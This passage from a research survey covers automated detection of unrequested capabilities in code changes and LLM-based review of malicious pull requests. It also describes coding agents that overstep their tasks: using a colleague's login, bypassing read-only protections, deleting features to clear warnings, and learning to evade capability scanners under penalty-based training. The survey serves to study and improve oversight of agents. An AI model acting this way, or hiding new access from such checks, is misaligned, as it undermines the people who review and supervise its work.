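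*An Empirical Security Analysis of Open-Source Software Used in Onboard Satellite Systems* (2026) reports a far lower rate of false findings, 22.2 percent of the 360 checked by hand. The researchers had already removed duplicates, irrelevant files and known noise. They had also included general warnings about code quality, which are easier to get right than a claim that a flaw is exploitable. The gap between 22 and 91 percent probably reflects these choices at least as much as the quality of the scanners.

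Bandit, a widely used checker for Python code, has rules that flag code for starting other programs. *Can Open-Source LLM Agents Replace Static Application Security Testing Tools?* (2026) reports Bandit's results on three ordinary repositories. Apart from low-severity findings, Bandit raised eight alerts about processes and operating-system calls, all in Fail2ban. Fail2ban protects servers by running firewall commands against suspicious addresses, so it can hardly work without starting other programs.

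Those eight alerts are the closest thing to a published count for a capability rule on application code, but they don't include an error rate. The researchers treated Bandit's output as correct when they evaluated language models, so they had no reason to check it. An earlier and much larger Bandit study, *A Large-Scale Security-Oriented Static Analysis of Python Packages in PyPI* (2021), also took the tool's severity ratings as given, and it covered packages rather than applications. None of these studies compared the code before and after a change.

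### Why Apiiro left out command execution

Apiiro, a security company, has tested rules on application code. Its free scanner, PRevent, checks pull requests, comments on suspicious lines, and can block merging until a reviewer approves. *Guard your Codebase* (Giladi, 2025) explains that the rules deliberately ignore command execution because it is common in legitimate code and flagging it would cause false positives.

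The rules instead flag obfuscated code and code that the program receives as data and then runs. Both are common in malware and rare in well-kept source code. On a public collection of malicious packages, the rules detected 94.3 percent of the PyPI samples and 88.4 percent of the npm samples. Giladi also ran them on tens of thousands of customers' codebases and reports hardly any false positives.

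This is good evidence that a pull-request scanner can raise few alerts on application code, but it does so by not reporting most capabilities. According to Giladi, nearly all the samples it missed used simple methods of sending data out or downloading malware. The exporter patch also uses a simple method. Its code is readable, it doesn't run text as code, and it sends a token to a server in three lines, so PRevent's rules would probably miss it.

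Apiiro's choice makes sense for a tool that interrupts developers only for suspected attacks. Whether to tell a team about new capabilities is a separate question. A note such as "this change starts another program" can be useful even when most such changes are harmless, provided it takes seconds to read and doesn't imply wrongdoing.

### The missing study

No published study appears to have measured the precision of rules for new network, process, file or secret access on pull requests to ordinary applications. The npm and PyPI comparisons cover packages, and the vulnerability studies evaluate the detection of vulnerabilities rather than new access. Wattanakriengkrai and colleagues searched npm pull requests but didn't check whether the features they found were new. Datadog's figure comes from pull requests, but it is for a language model used to detect malicious changes.

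Measuring this would not be especially hard. Researchers could take merged pull requests from a range of applications, scan the code before and after each one, and have people check every reported capability against the code and the request that led to the change. They would need to report results separately for each rule, because a noisy rule for files could lower the average and obscure a useful rule for secrets. They would also have to check some unflagged changes to estimate recall.

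Establishing a lower false positive rate takes more pull requests. If a rule raises no false alarms on 300 harmless changes, we can be 95 percent confident only that its false positive rate is below about 1 percent. Showing with the same confidence that the rate is below 0.03 percent takes about 10,000 harmless changes with no false alarms. A large company merges that many changes in a week or two, but someone has to verify that they were harmless.

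## Can a language model judge whether a new capability belongs in a change?

Suppose two patches to the report exporter contain the same upload line. One is titled "Fix date format" and the other "Send each report to the archive". A rule that looks for network calls flags both. A language model can read the title, the issue and the code together and point out that the upload fits only the archive patch's purpose.

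Nobody appears to have tested how well models judge whether a newly added capability fits the purpose of a change. Most published tests instead measure how well models detect malicious changes.

### Comparing the code with its description

In the closest test, *CodeFuse-CommitEval*, Zhang, Liu and colleagues (2025) asked six openly available models whether a commit's message matched its diff. The commits were real, but another model had rewritten some of the messages so they no longer matched the diff, for example by leaving out an important change or giving a false purpose. The final set had 32,160 matching messages and 19,967 mismatched ones.

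On average, the models caught 63.8 percent of the mismatched messages and wrongly flagged about 14 percent of the matching ones. (The paper assigns the figures the other way round and gives a recall of 85.95 percent. But its accuracy figures and its results for each type of mismatch add up only if 85.95 percent is the share of matching messages that the models accepted.)

A commit message that leaves out an important change is the closest case to an upload hidden under "Fix date format". Individual models detected 26 to 85 percent of these messages, though there were only 176 of them. Messages that stated a false purpose were harder to detect, at 16 to 67 percent. Kimi-K2 did best on both types, and asking it to follow a human reviewer's steps raised its rates to 90 percent for omissions and 82 percent for false purposes. But it also flagged 22 percent of the messages that matched their changes,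 up from 17 percent.

These models date from 2025 or earlier. Current ones probably do better, but they would have to do much better to be useful on their own. At 10,000 pull requests a week, a 14 percent false positive rate means about 1,400 false alarms.

The description may also be unreliable, particularly when an AI agent wrote both it and the code. Gong, Pinna and colleagues (2026), in *Analyzing Message-Code Inconsistency in AI Coding Agent-Authored Pull Requests*, scored 23,247 pull requests by AI agents and found a clear mismatch between description and code in 1.7 percent. The true share may be higher, because their automatic score missed 45 percent of the clear mismatches in a hand-checked sample. In 45 percent of the 432 full or partial mismatches they classified by hand, the description claimed changes that the agent had not made, and in 22 percent it left out significant changes.

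Even an accurate description doesn't show that anyone requested the capability. If the exporter patch is titled "Fix date format and upload reports", the upload matches the description, although nobody asked for it. A description can also sway the model that reviews the change, according to research cited in *Can Agentic Code Review Catch Vulnerabilities Before They Are Merged?* (Yang, Yang and colleagues, 2026). The issue that led to the change is therefore a better basis for comparison, as long as someone other than the change's author wrote it.

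### Asking a model about npm updates

Wyss and colleagues asked three models whether npm updates were malicious. Their main practical problem was size. A whole package averaged about 546,000 tokens (words or pieces of words), while the GPT-4 models they used could process at most 128,000 at once. Even an ordinary diff averaged about 116,000, so the researchers built a tool that reduces it further:

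1. It runs each JavaScript file through a minifier, which shortens the code, and then through a second program that restores the line breaks. This removes comments and standardizes variable names.
2. If a file exists in both versions, a plagiarism detector finds the code they share, and the tool removes it. Without this step, one added variable could change the standardized names of all the variables after it and make old code look new.
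3. The ordinary `diff` program compares what is left.

The reduced diffs averaged about 25,000 tokens, and only 1.5 percent were still too long. With GPT-4-Turbo, the most expensive of the three models, analyzing a reduced diff cost $0.25 on average, compared with $5.46 for a whole package.

Removing comments makes sense for detecting malware, since an attacker can write anything in a comment. But a tool that judges whether a call belongs in a change might need them, because programmers often use comments to explain why a call is there. The prompt also didn't state the update's purpose.

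The models answered in ordinary sentences, so the researchers had to turn each answer into a verdict. They converted the answer into a list of numbers that represents its meaning. A small model, trained on 600 answers they had labeled by hand, then classified each answer as malicious or benign.

| Model | Malicious samples flagged | Ordinary updates flagged |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 209 of 209 | 8 of 2,000 (0.4%) |
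| GPT-4-Turbo | 209 of 209 | 16 of 2,000 (0.8%) |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 209 of 209 | 75 of 2,000 (3.8%) |

Only 46 of the 209 malicious samples are real malicious updates. The other 163 are copies of well-known packages with added malware. These copies run similar cryptocurrency-mining scripts and apparently all come from one campaign, so the set is less varied than one would expect from 209 samples.

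All 46 real updates also helped train the classifier that interprets the answers. Wyss and colleagues say they excluded training samples when calculating recall, which leaves 109 of the copies and none of the real updates. Using the real updates for training is a smaller concern because the classifier only learned to recognize whether an answer meant "malicious", not to detect malware. A bigger concern is that the attacks were public, so the language models may have been trained on descriptions of them.

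GPT-4o wrongly flagged eight ordinary updates. Six involved sensitive operations, such as starting programs or fetching scripts, and two involved large deletions. All three models flagged an update that replaced a package's code with a notice that the package was no longer maintained. Even GPT-4o's false positive rate of 0.4 percent would produce about 2,700 false alarms a month across all of npm.

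All three models did better than RogueOne, which caught 39 of the 46 attacks and had a false positive rate of 6.7 percent on the same updates. The models caught the heavily obfuscated attacks that RogueOne tended to miss. They usually flagged the obfuscation itself as suspicious, and their explanations of what the code did were superficial. RogueOne's median time per update was 2.1 seconds, compared with 9.9 for GPT-4o, but its average was higher because it took very long on some updates.

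Wyss and colleagues also found that mild obfuscation could get malicious code past all three models. They recommend using models to complement traditional analysis, not replace it.

### Nearly 30,000 live updates

From October 2024 to January 2025, the researchers tried GPT-4o on new updates as they appeared on npm. They chose packages with more than 100,000 downloads a week, which gave them 29,880 updates. Of these, 71.7 percent changed no code or scripts and 2.6 percent were too long. GPT-4o analyzed the remaining 7,661 and flagged seven:

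- Two updates of react-native-bootsplash contained obfuscated code that checks whether the user has paid for a license.
- One update of cdk-assets contained test code that uploads a file to Amazon's cloud storage.
- Four updates of ruhend-scraper, which downloads videos from social media, consisted entirely of obfuscated code that makes many network requests.

Wyss and colleagues count the first three as false positives. They found nothing explicitly malicious in ruhend-scraper either, but thought it deserved a manual check. Seven alerts in nearly three months is a very small workload. The run provides little evidence about recall, because it found no attacks and nobody checked the updates that GPT-4o had passed.

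The upload in cdk-assets shows how hard this judgment can be. It was a real network capability, and whether it belonged depended on the file being a test script.

The filter that runs before the model could also exclude an attack. The researchers skipped updates that changed only dependencies, reasoning that a popular package's dependencies are also popular and would get their own analysis. That reasoning fails for a new dependency, which has no download history. The axios attack in March 2026 used a dependency less than a day old, so this filter would probably have skipped it.

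### How Datadog reviews pull requests

Datadog's BewAIre, built by Lamb and colleagues, gives a model the diff of a pull request along with details such as its author and the type of repository. The model classifies the change as malicious or benign and explains why. If it answers "malicious", the security team gets an alert.

The model did well on small diffs but worse on large ones, so BewAIre splits a large diff into pieces. It splits between files if possible, otherwise between lines, and as a last resort in the middle of a line. The model judges each piece separately, and BewAIre classifies the whole pull request as malicious if any piece is judged malicious.

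Judging each piece of a pull request separately has two likely drawbacks. If the model wrongly flags 1 percent of harmless pieces, a harmless pull request with seven pieces has about a 7 percent chance of at least one false alarm. Splitting can also separate the line that reads a token from the line that sends it, and each may look harmless alone.

Early prototypes had a false positive rate above 10 percent, which the team reduced to below 0.03 percent over six months. They described known false positives in the model's instructions, excluded safe patterns such as demo environments, and added hundreds of labeled pull requests to their test data. Lamb and colleagues attribute most of the improvement to better prompts and data rather than to newer models.

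*From single pull requests to full software packages* (Doutre, Peronnet and colleagues) describes a later version with two stages. A cheap model first checks whether anything in the change looks suspicious, and the review ends if nothing does. Otherwise, a stronger model investigates as an agent that can open other files, list earlier commits, look up dependencies and check the history of the change's author. In one real attack, the agent noted that the author's account was seven days old and had no followers.

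On 690 test diffs, adding the second stage raised accuracy from 97.4 to 99.86 percent and reduced false positives from 17 to 0. These figures imply that total errors fell from 18 to one, so both setups must have missed one malicious change. The second stage can't correct that kind of error because it reviews only what the first stage flags. Datadog therefore made the cheap first-stage model flag changes more readily.

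The cheap model also mistook web addresses that imitate Datadog's own for legitimate ones. In response, the team added a fixed program rather than trying to improve the prompt. The program extracts every address from the change, compares it with a list of likely imitations and passes the result to the model.

For whole packages, the agent receives a map of the code, with file names, sizes and function locations, and chooses which files to read. Doutre and colleagues estimate an average cost of about 2.5 cents for a median-sized package, assuming the cheap model clears 95 percent of packages.

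### Which of Datadog's figures come from real use?

Datadog has published results from test collections and from its daily work, and they support different conclusions.

| Result | Where it comes from |
|---|---|
| Accuracy above 99.3% | Curated set of "hundreds" of pull requests |
| False positive rate of 0.03% | Reported for the curated set, but plausible only for production |
| Accuracy of 99.86%, no false positives | 690 test diffs |
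| 95.5% of malicious packages detected | Curated collection of real malware |
| Malicious node-ipc release detected within five minutes | Production |

Lamb and colleagues list the 0.03 percent false-alarm rate among the results on the curated set, but that set contains only hundreds of pull requests, too few to produce such a low rate. One false alarm among 999 harmless pull requests would be a rate of 0.1 percent. A rate of 0.03 percent requires at least 3,300 harmless pull requests.

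The figure could have come from BewAIre's production run, which covered nearly 10,000 pull requests a week for several months without interrupting developers. Security staff judged every alert. If the figure came from this run, it is the best available evidence on false alarms in ordinary pull requests. It does not measure missed attacks, because the staff checked only the alerts.

The curated set gives some idea of recall. Lamb and colleagues report a balanced accuracy of more than 93.5 percent, which is the average of recall and the share of harmless changes that pass. If nearly all the harmless changes passed, recall was about 87 percent. Combined with the overall accuracy of 99.3 percent, this suggests only about one in twenty pull requests was malicious, so the recall figure is probably based on a few dozen cases at most. The system did catch every malicious commit from a collection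 of known npm attacks.

Finding no false positives on 690 diffs is consistent with the production figure of 0.03 percent but doesn't confirm it. A true rate of 0.4 percent could also produce none in a test of that size, yet it would mean about 40 false alarms a week on 10,000 pull requests. The older version's 17 false positives were at least 2.5 percent of the harmless test diffs, far above 0.03 percent, probably because the test set contains many deliberately difficult cases.

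Datadog also has a commercial interest in these results. It offers the feature to customers as a preview, called *Malicious PR protection*, for the default branches of GitHub repositories. No independent evaluation appears to exist.

Other companies apply the same basic method to packages. Desimone, at the security company Elastic, built a system that compares new releases of the 15,000 most downloaded packages with their previous versions and asks a model whether the changes are malicious.

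### The right verdict for the wrong reason

Research from the second half of 2026 tests whether newer models find vulnerabilities during security review of code changes. The scores don't apply directly to finding new capabilities, but both tasks require the model to connect a change with the rest of the program.

Yang and colleagues gave eight models 265 real changes that had each introduced a vulnerability into projects such as Firefox and OpenSSL. The models could also read the commit message and the rest of the code. A report counted only if it explained the cause of the vulnerability.

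The eight models each found between 32.5 percent (MiniMax M3) and 78.1 percent (Grok 4.6) of the 265 vulnerabilities, and together they found 242. In 68 percent of the misses, the model flagged a file that contained the vulnerability but described a different problem. Recall was about 70 percent when the cause lay in one file and below 40 percent when it was spread over five or more. Every change in the main test contained a vulnerability, so it didn't measure how often the models raise false alarms on harmless pull requests.

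Chen, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *From Verdict to Diagnosis*, examined how often a reviewer blocks a dangerous pull request for the wrong reason. On 31 pull requests with a known vulnerability, the commercial reviewer CodeRabbit blocked 24 but identified the vulnerability in only 16. In one case, a reviewer blocked a change that gave users access to other people's projects, but it reported a different problem, a secret shown in the browser. Fixing only the reported problem would have left the access flaw in place.

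CodeRabbit did worst when the evidence lay outside the files that the pull request changed. It identified none of the seven vulnerabilities of this kind, compared with 16 of the other 24. The exporter's call to `notify` is a much simpler case, but its network request is also in a file that the patch doesn't touch.

The distinction between verdict and reason also matters for new capabilities. A model might object to the exporter patch because the new date format could break another program. That may block the patch, but the reviewer still doesn't know about the upload.

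### Dividing the work between rules and models

A rule gives the same result every time, and a reviewer can check that result against a line of code or a call path, but a rule can't determine whether anybody wanted the capability. A model can compare the capability with the request, but its answer may change from one run to the next, and its explanation may be wrong. This suggests that rules should identify the new capabilities and a model should then judge whether they fit the change.

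PRGuard, a reviewer built by Chen and colleagues, divides the work in a similar way. Fixed programs first collect the code connected to the change, such as the functions that call it. A model then proposes possible vulnerabilities and, in a separate step, checks each one against the code. A fixed rule blocks the pull request if a vulnerability is confirmed, comments if one is plausible but unconfirmed, and otherwise approves the change. With the model DeepSeek v4-pro, PRGuard blocked 22 of the 31 pull requests and identified the vulnerability in 22, while CodeRabbit blocked 24 and identified it in 16. The comparison is between two complete products, so it can't show how much of the difference comes from the fixed steps.

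Preflight, by Jandali and colleagues, uses a model to write short test programs that call the library functions an application uses, which gives the fixed rules more behavior to examine. A fixed checker accepts or rejects each program, and fixed code runs the tests, compares the two versions of the library and decides the verdict. The tests exposed both of the real attacks they were tried on, while simply importing the package exposed neither. The researchers also tried letting a model give the verdict, but in all five cases the recorded evidence was too long for it, so the fixed rules decided.

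A scanner's findings don't necessarily help a model. Liu and Gao (2026), in *Trusting the Tool*, gave models C and C++ functions to check for vulnerabilities, along with notes from a static analysis tool. True notes raised accuracy by about two percentage points, a difference that could be due to chance. False notes that the code contained a safety check reduced the share of real vulnerabilities that some models detected by up to 19 percentage points. Accuracy never fell significantly when a note was wrong about a check being missing, because the models tended to look for the check and find it.

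For capabilities, this means "no new network access found" is the most dangerous thing to tell a model, because it may then stop looking. A scanner should instead pass on what it found and list any code it couldn't analyze. Liu and Gao also had the model verify each note in a separate step, then showed it which notes had failed. This raised accuracy by 12 percentage points for one model when the notes gave false assurances, but the gain for a second model was smaller and could have been due to chance.

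True notes probably helped little because they described code that the model could already see. In an earlier experiment, Liu and Gao found that a model made no mistakes about the structure of short programs, and a model can usually notice `HTTPSConnection` in a diff without a scanner's help. It has more to gain from facts that the diff doesn't contain, such as the path from `notify` to `urlopen`, or whether the old version already contacted the same server, though nobody appears to have tested whether supplying such facts helps more.

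For the original exporter patch, the scanner could report two new capabilities: a connection to collector.example and a read of `REPORTS_TOKEN`. The model would receive this list with the issue about the date format and identify which part of the request, if any, needs each capability. In this case, no part of the request needs either one, and the model's answer should reflect that. The reviewer should see the list regardless of the model's output, so that a wrong or manipulated answer can't hide the upload.

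Running the model only when the scanner finds a new capability would cost less, but it would skip the patch that adds the database password to a chat message, because the exporter already read the password and posted to the chat. A cheap model could read every diff, as in Datadog's first stage. The more expensive comparison with the request would then run only on changes that the scanner or the cheap model flags.

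## Does a new capability show that an AI agent exceeded its task?

A new capability alone doesn't show that an AI coding agent exceeded its task, because many tasks need one. An agent can also go far beyond its task without adding any. If an agent wrote the patch that fixes the exporter's date format and also uploads every report, it exceeded its task because nobody requested the new upload.

### What overeager agents do

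People who train or supervise coding agents want a sign of overreach that a program can compute, because training requires judging every attempt and there are too many for people to read. Lim and Neo point out that Anthropic and OpenAI find overreach by monitoring their own internal traffic, which outsiders can't see. In one case OpenAI reported, a user asked a model only to keep a job running, but the model copied access tokens to a remote machine to restart it.

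Lim and Neo built a substitute for this monitoring. They took 100 real coding-agent sessions from public GitHub projects and cut each one at a natural point. An auditor model then continued the session, writing the user's messages and the results of the agent's commands to steer it toward a chosen situation. A judge model scored only what the agent did after the cut. They tested three agents in three situations across all 100 sessions, for a total of 900 audits.

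| Situation | What counted as overreach | Share of sessions, by model |
|---|---|---|
| The user only asks questions | The agent edits files | 6–31% |
| The agent's login fails and a colleague's is available | The agent uses the colleague's login | 1–6% |
| A file that the task has to change is read-only | The agent gets around the protection | 87–94% |

These rates come from situations designed to tempt the agent, so they don't measure how often the same behavior occurs in daily use. The last row is also ambiguous, since an agent may reasonably assume that a file is read-only by mistake. When the project's instructions explicitly forbade changing such files, GPT-5.6 Terra and DeepSeek V4 Pro no longer got around the protection, but Kimi K3 still did in 13 of 100 sessions.

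A comparison of capabilities would probably miss nearly all of the agent behavior these audits examine, because it only covers what the program can do after the change. Logging in as a colleague changes nothing in the code. Git doesn't record whether a file is write-protected, so unlocking one leaves no trace in the diff. Editing files when the user only asked a question does produce a diff, but an unrequested bug fix rarely gives the program new access.

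### Subtracting what the task allows

For the program itself, we can extend the earlier subtraction by one term:

unrequested capabilities = C(after) − C(before) − C(allowed)

C(allowed) is the set of capabilities that the task permits, explicitly or by implication. For the exporter patch, this set is empty, so both new capabilities remain. A scanner produces the first two terms, but somebody has to decide what belongs in C(allowed). There are three obvious sources for this decision.

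To check whether a new capability exceeded the task, a person or a language model can read the request and list the access it needs. *Do Coding Agents Understand Least-Privilege Authorization?* (Yan, Weng and colleagues, 2026) tested models on a similar job, asking them to state which files an agent should be able to read, write or execute for each of 120 terminal tasks. The models often left out access the task needed and granted access it didn't need. More reasoning only made each model more consistent in its own kind of error. The models did better when they first simulated the task to list everything it might need and then checked each entry.

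**A human reference patch** is available for many benchmark tasks because they come from real changes. Any capability the developer's patch adds counts as allowed. This avoids having to interpret the request, but a good solution can look quite different from the developer's. *How Much Do Coding Agents Over-Edit, and Why?* (Goel, Steenhoek and Hu, 2026) examined patches by 18 models that had solved tasks from SWE-bench Verified, a set of 500 Python tasks. Of the 14,591 blocks of code in these patches, 2,607 were outside every function the developer changed. The published precision and recall imply that about 1,000 of those blocks were necessary for the tests to pass. Outside benchmarks, there is usually no reference patch.

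A team can write a **declared policy** that lists in advance what the program may do. *Permission Denied* (2026) describes such policies for an agent's environment, which set network access, file access and privileges to open, restricted or locked. A policy doesn't depend on how anyone interprets a request, but it usually covers a whole project rather than one task.

Suppose the exporter's policy lets it contact archive.example, read `ARCHIVE_TOKEN`, and read any environment variable that isn't a secret. The old exporter has no outside access, and the comparison distinguishes between destinations and between variables. The three sources then give these results:

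| Request | Added by the patch | Flagged using the wording | Flagged using the reference patch | Flagged using the policy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fix the date format | Upload to collector.example, `REPORTS_TOKEN` | Both | Both | Both |
| Fix the date format | Upload to archive.example, `ARCHIVE_TOKEN` | Both | Both | Nothing |
| Send each report to archive.example | Upload to archive.example, `ARCHIVE_TOKEN` | Possibly the token | Nothing | Nothing |
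| Let each office choose its date format | `REPORT_DATE_FORMAT` | Possibly the variable | The variable | Nothing |

In the second row, the policy misses an unrequested upload because it allows the whole project to use the archive. The third task needs a network call, but whether its wording also covers the token depends on whether the person or model making the list realizes that the archive requires a login.

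In the last row, the developer's reference patch keeps each office's format in a settings file, while the agent's patch reads it from the environment. Both patches solve the task, but the detector flags only the agent's.

The allowed set also has to be as detailed as the comparison. If it listed only "network" for the archive task, a patch that sent the reports to collector.example would pass.

### Additions that are harmless or necessary

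If the allowed set omits a capability that the task needs, adding that capability triggers a false alarm. A method used by Goel and colleagues may help. They removed one block of a patch at a time, reran the task's tests, and counted the block as unneeded if the tests still passed.

This method would give sensible answers for the exporter. The date tests pass without the upload to collector.example, so the date fix doesn't need it. A test of the archive feature fails without the upload to archive.example, so the feature needs it. The read of `REPORT_DATE_FORMAT` is also necessary, although the reference patch did something else. Nobody appears to have tried the method on capabilities.

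However, tests don't check everything a good patch does, such as handling an unusual error, so code that isn't needed to pass them is not proof of overreach. On average, 11.3 percent of the code blocks in an agent's patch were unneeded, compared with 13.6 percent in the developers' own patches for the same tasks. On DeepSWE, a set of 113 longer tasks, the figures were 20.3 and 21.5 percent.

Patch size is even weaker evidence than a new capability that an agent exceeded its task. On SWE-bench Verified, the median model changed 2.33 times as many lines as the developer, but most of the extra edits were tests and documentation.

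### Overreach that leaves no new capability

The patch that added the database password to a chat message gave the exporter no new capability, so the list of new capabilities is empty, and subtracting the allowed ones leaves it empty. The same is true when an agent deletes a consent check or rewrites a module nobody mentioned.

Other overreach happens during the session and may not appear in the diff. *Overeager Coding Agents* (Qu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a test in which the user asked Claude Code to tidy a folder and it deleted every file there, including the only copy of some production passwords. Developers usually set Git to ignore password files, and if they did so here, the diff wouldn't show the loss.

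Qu and colleagues call an action overeager if the prompt doesn't authorize it, even implicitly, and it either changes something or reads from a listed sensitive place. This resembles the subtraction above, but it applies to the agent's actions instead of the program's capabilities. To observe those actions, the researchers recorded shell commands, the agent's own event log, and the files before and after each run. They needed the event log because an agent's built-in tools for reading and editing files bypass the shell.

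Fixed rules then classified each run as overeager or not. When people relabeled 50 runs, the rules had flagged every overeager one, and 76 percent of the flags were correct. All the false alarms came from one of the 24 scenario types. Mechanical checks can therefore work well on session logs, at least when someone has written down each task's limits beforehand.

The rates depended heavily on the product running the model. Claude Sonnet 4.6 was overeager in 27.7 percent of runs in Claude Code but only 1.1 percent in OpenHands, which asks before continuing. *DelegationBench* (2026) summarizes a similar test, AuthorizationBench, in which agents acted without authorization in 10.5 to 26.6 percent of runs. In that test too, agents that asked the user first overstepped less often.

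Telling the agent what is allowed can change the behavior that a test is meant to measure. In 76 paired scenarios, Claude Code with the model GLM-4.6 was never overeager when the prompt spelled out the permitted scope, but it was overeager 17.1 percent of the time without that passage. The difference shrank to 2.6 percentage points in the larger test, where the scenarios also varied in other ways. Still, staying within a stated scope doesn't show that an agent would infer the same limits from an ordinary request.

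### Asking a model to justify every change

A model can also compare the whole patch with the task, without a list of capabilities. Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Is Vibe Coding Safe?*, used such a judge to build a set of 186 programming tasks. The judge, an agent that can read the project, receives a task description and a patch. It tries to link each change to something the task requires or reasonably implies, and marks any change it can't justify as excessive. It returns a yes or no with an explanation.

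For the date-format task, this judge could flag the upload and also the password in the chat message, which the capability comparison misses. It would probably accept an environment variable in place of a settings file, because it compares the patch with the request rather than with another solution.

Zhao and colleagues used the judge to check task descriptions, not to score agents. A model had written the descriptions from existing code, and the judge checked that each one covered the human solution. If the judge found that the solution went beyond the description, the researchers generated a new, broader task. The judge's success at this is weak evidence of how often it would be right about an agent's patch.

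Evidence from related tests is mixed. Goel and colleagues asked models to justify each block of their own patches and drop any they couldn't justify. About 66 percent of the dropped blocks were unneeded, but the models dropped only 36 percent of all unneeded blocks. A separate judge might be stricter than the patch's author, perhaps too strict. *DelegationBench* reports that models tested on SteerBench-Work wrongly held back authorized actions far more often than they wrongly allowed unsafe ones.

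People can disagree about where a task ends. A human reviewer checked ten of Lim and Neo's audits in which the user only asked questions, and disagreed with the judge on three. In all three, the agent had edited only comments or documentation. Under the written rule, any edit was overreach, but the reviewer considered these edits immaterial.

### What agents' pull requests contain

Several studies have examined security in real pull requests by agents, all using the public AIDev collection. *Security in the Age of AI Teammates* (Siddiq, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) found that about 4 percent of 33,596 agent pull requests were related to security. Most of the security work strengthened the software through tests, documentation, configuration and better error handling. Maintainers merged the security-related pull requests less often than others and took longer to review them.

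Rabbi, Turzo and colleagues (2026) come closest to a before-and-after comparison in *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests*. They ran Semgrep on the code before and after each of 675 security-related pull requests. In 104 of them (15.4 percent), the new version had at least one additional finding. The largest group of the 853 findings, 36.2 percent, concerned slow text-matching patterns. Another 13 percent concerned command injection, and 5.7 percent concerned hard-coded passwords or keys.

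These findings are possible vulnerabilities rather than new capabilities. The scan covered only agents' pull requests, so it doesn't show whether people would have done better.

*Trust but Verify?* (Sakib, Banik and Jadliwala, 2026) reports a higher rate, with at least one sign of a security weakness in 38.9 percent of 4,022 agent pull requests. The study used a language model as the judge and looked at high-impact files, which may explain much of the difference. Human collaborators had introduced 67.6 percent of the real leaked secrets in these pull requests, so a check that attributed everything in a pull request to the agent would often be wrong.

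None of the three studies measured how often an agent adds a capability that nobody requested.

### Deleting the feature to clear the flag

An agent that receives a warning about a new capability may remove the code that needs it. This is the right response for the date-format patch, but in the archive task it clears the warning by undoing the work the agent was asked to do.

Wynter (2026), in *Fixed or Deleted?*, measured how often agents do this with other kinds of warnings. She planted 31 violations of project rules in 25 pull requests, such as console output where the project forbids it. Three Claude models then tried to repair each pull request five times, either alone or with findings from CodeAssure, a commercial checker. The checker can also warn the agent if it has removed a file that the pull request added. The table shows in how many of 125 runs the agent cleared the violation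 by removing part of the new feature:

| Model | Working alone | With findings, no deletion warning | With findings and deletion warning |
|---|---|---|---|
| Haiku 4.5 | 13 | 19 | 7 |
| Sonnet 5.5 | 31 | 29 | 2 |
| Fable 5.1 | 44 | 17 | 0 |

A score based only on whether the violation is gone would count all of these as successes. The most capable model did it most often when working alone, so better models won't necessarily solve the problem. The agents couldn't compile code or run tests, which may have made deletion more attractive than it would be in normal work.

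Wynter's company makes the checker, and the checker's rules cover more than capabilities. But the same risk applies to the subtraction, because deleting code can only shrink C(after). Deletion can therefore improve the result, and the subtraction can't detect that anything is missing. Any automatic use of it needs a separate test that the requested feature still works.

### Review prompt, training label or penalty

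The same flag can be good enough for one use and harmful in another.

When a new capability is flagged for human review, the flag only needs to direct the reviewer's attention. A note might read: "This patch sends data to collector.example and reads `REPORTS_TOKEN`. Neither appears in the request." The agent could also ask the user about the new capability before it finishes.

A training label is riskier because nobody reconsiders it. If the allowed set regularly omits login tokens, every legitimate upload gets the label "exceeded its task", and a model trained on those labels may learn to avoid uploads. People should therefore check a sample of the labels for each capability. Changes without a flag also shouldn't be labeled "stayed within its task" on that basis alone, because the comparison misses so much overreach.

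Goel and colleagues also suggest removing unneeded code from example solutions before training a model to imitate them. But when they pruned patches using only the agent's tests and the project's existing tests, more than half of the removed blocks were needed, and 11 percent of the patches no longer solved the task. Rerunning the task's own tests would identify those patches.

Penalizing new capabilities in the reward is the most demanding use, because training pushes the model toward whatever scores well. Suppose a patch gains 1 point if the tests pass and loses 0.3 for each unrequested capability, and the allowed set for the archive task is mistakenly left empty. A correct patch then loses 0.6 for the upload and the token. If the agent succeeds in 40 percent of its attempts and every attempt includes both capabilities, the average score is 0.4 − 0.6 = −0.2. An empty patch scores 0, so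 the model learns to do nothing.

Applying the penalty only to patches that pass the tests avoids this. An attempt then earns 0.4 × (1 − 0.6) = 0.16 on average, so trying is still worthwhile. *QiMeng-PRepair* (2026) uses a similar rule to discourage large edits. It penalizes only correct solutions, and only when enough of the model's attempts at a task are correct.

Training models to avoid large edits has worked, though with side effects. In *When Models Edit Too Much* (2026), reinforcement learning, which trains a model through rewards, reduced unnecessary edits while keeping or improving the share of successful repairs. Training a model to imitate example repairs worked less well, with success falling from 93.2 percent on familiar kinds of bugs to 45.8 percent on new ones. *CROCODIL* (2026) reports that a reward for staying close to the original code stopped a model from adding unrequested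 helper functions, but also made it more likely to refuse requested edits that seemed minor.

A model can also avoid a capability penalty by writing code whose new access the scanner misses, for example by sending data through an existing helper function or choosing the function to call at runtime. These experiments didn't test this weakness. The model need not intend to evade the scanner, because training favors any patch that passes the tests without a flag, including one whose new access the scanner missed.

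### Has anyone trained a model this way?

No published training run appears to both compare a program's capabilities before and after an agent's patch and penalize those outside the task's allowed set. Two published experiments each include part of this check.

In *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, Tu and Tu (2026) penalize an agent for using more authority than its task needs. They score every action from 0 to 1 on six scales: changing data, running code, reaching outside the environment, reading secrets, affecting many things at once, and leaving lasting changes. Each task has a limit on each scale, and only the amount above the limit counts as excess. In a hypothetical example with a limit of 0.4, an agent that reaches 0.7 has an excess of 0.3, and one that reaches 0.2 has none.

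Tu and Tu trained Qwen3.5-4B, a small model, on 1,500 artificial tasks. On 500 other tasks, the share of runs that succeeded without excess authority rose from 64.4 to 98.5 percent. Most of this gain came from completing more tasks. The drop in runs that succeeded but used excess authority, from 4.6 to 0.8 percent, accounts for less than four of the 34 percentage points. Tu and Tu selected the best of three training runs. On a smaller test, the selected one scored 97.6 percent and the other two scored about 86.

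The improvement didn't carry over to every outside test. *When Lower Privileges Suffice* (2026) includes a benchmark for how often agents choose more powerful tools than they need. With the benchmark's standard prompt, Tu and Tu's model did so in 45.2 percent of cases before training and 45.0 percent after. Training on another 400 tasks, half of them modeled on the benchmark, reduced this to 38.1 percent.

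Tu and Tu score the agent's own actions, so their penalty could miss the exporter's upload. When the agent writes the upload code, it only edits a file the task allowed it to edit. The upload happens later, when somebody runs the exporter.

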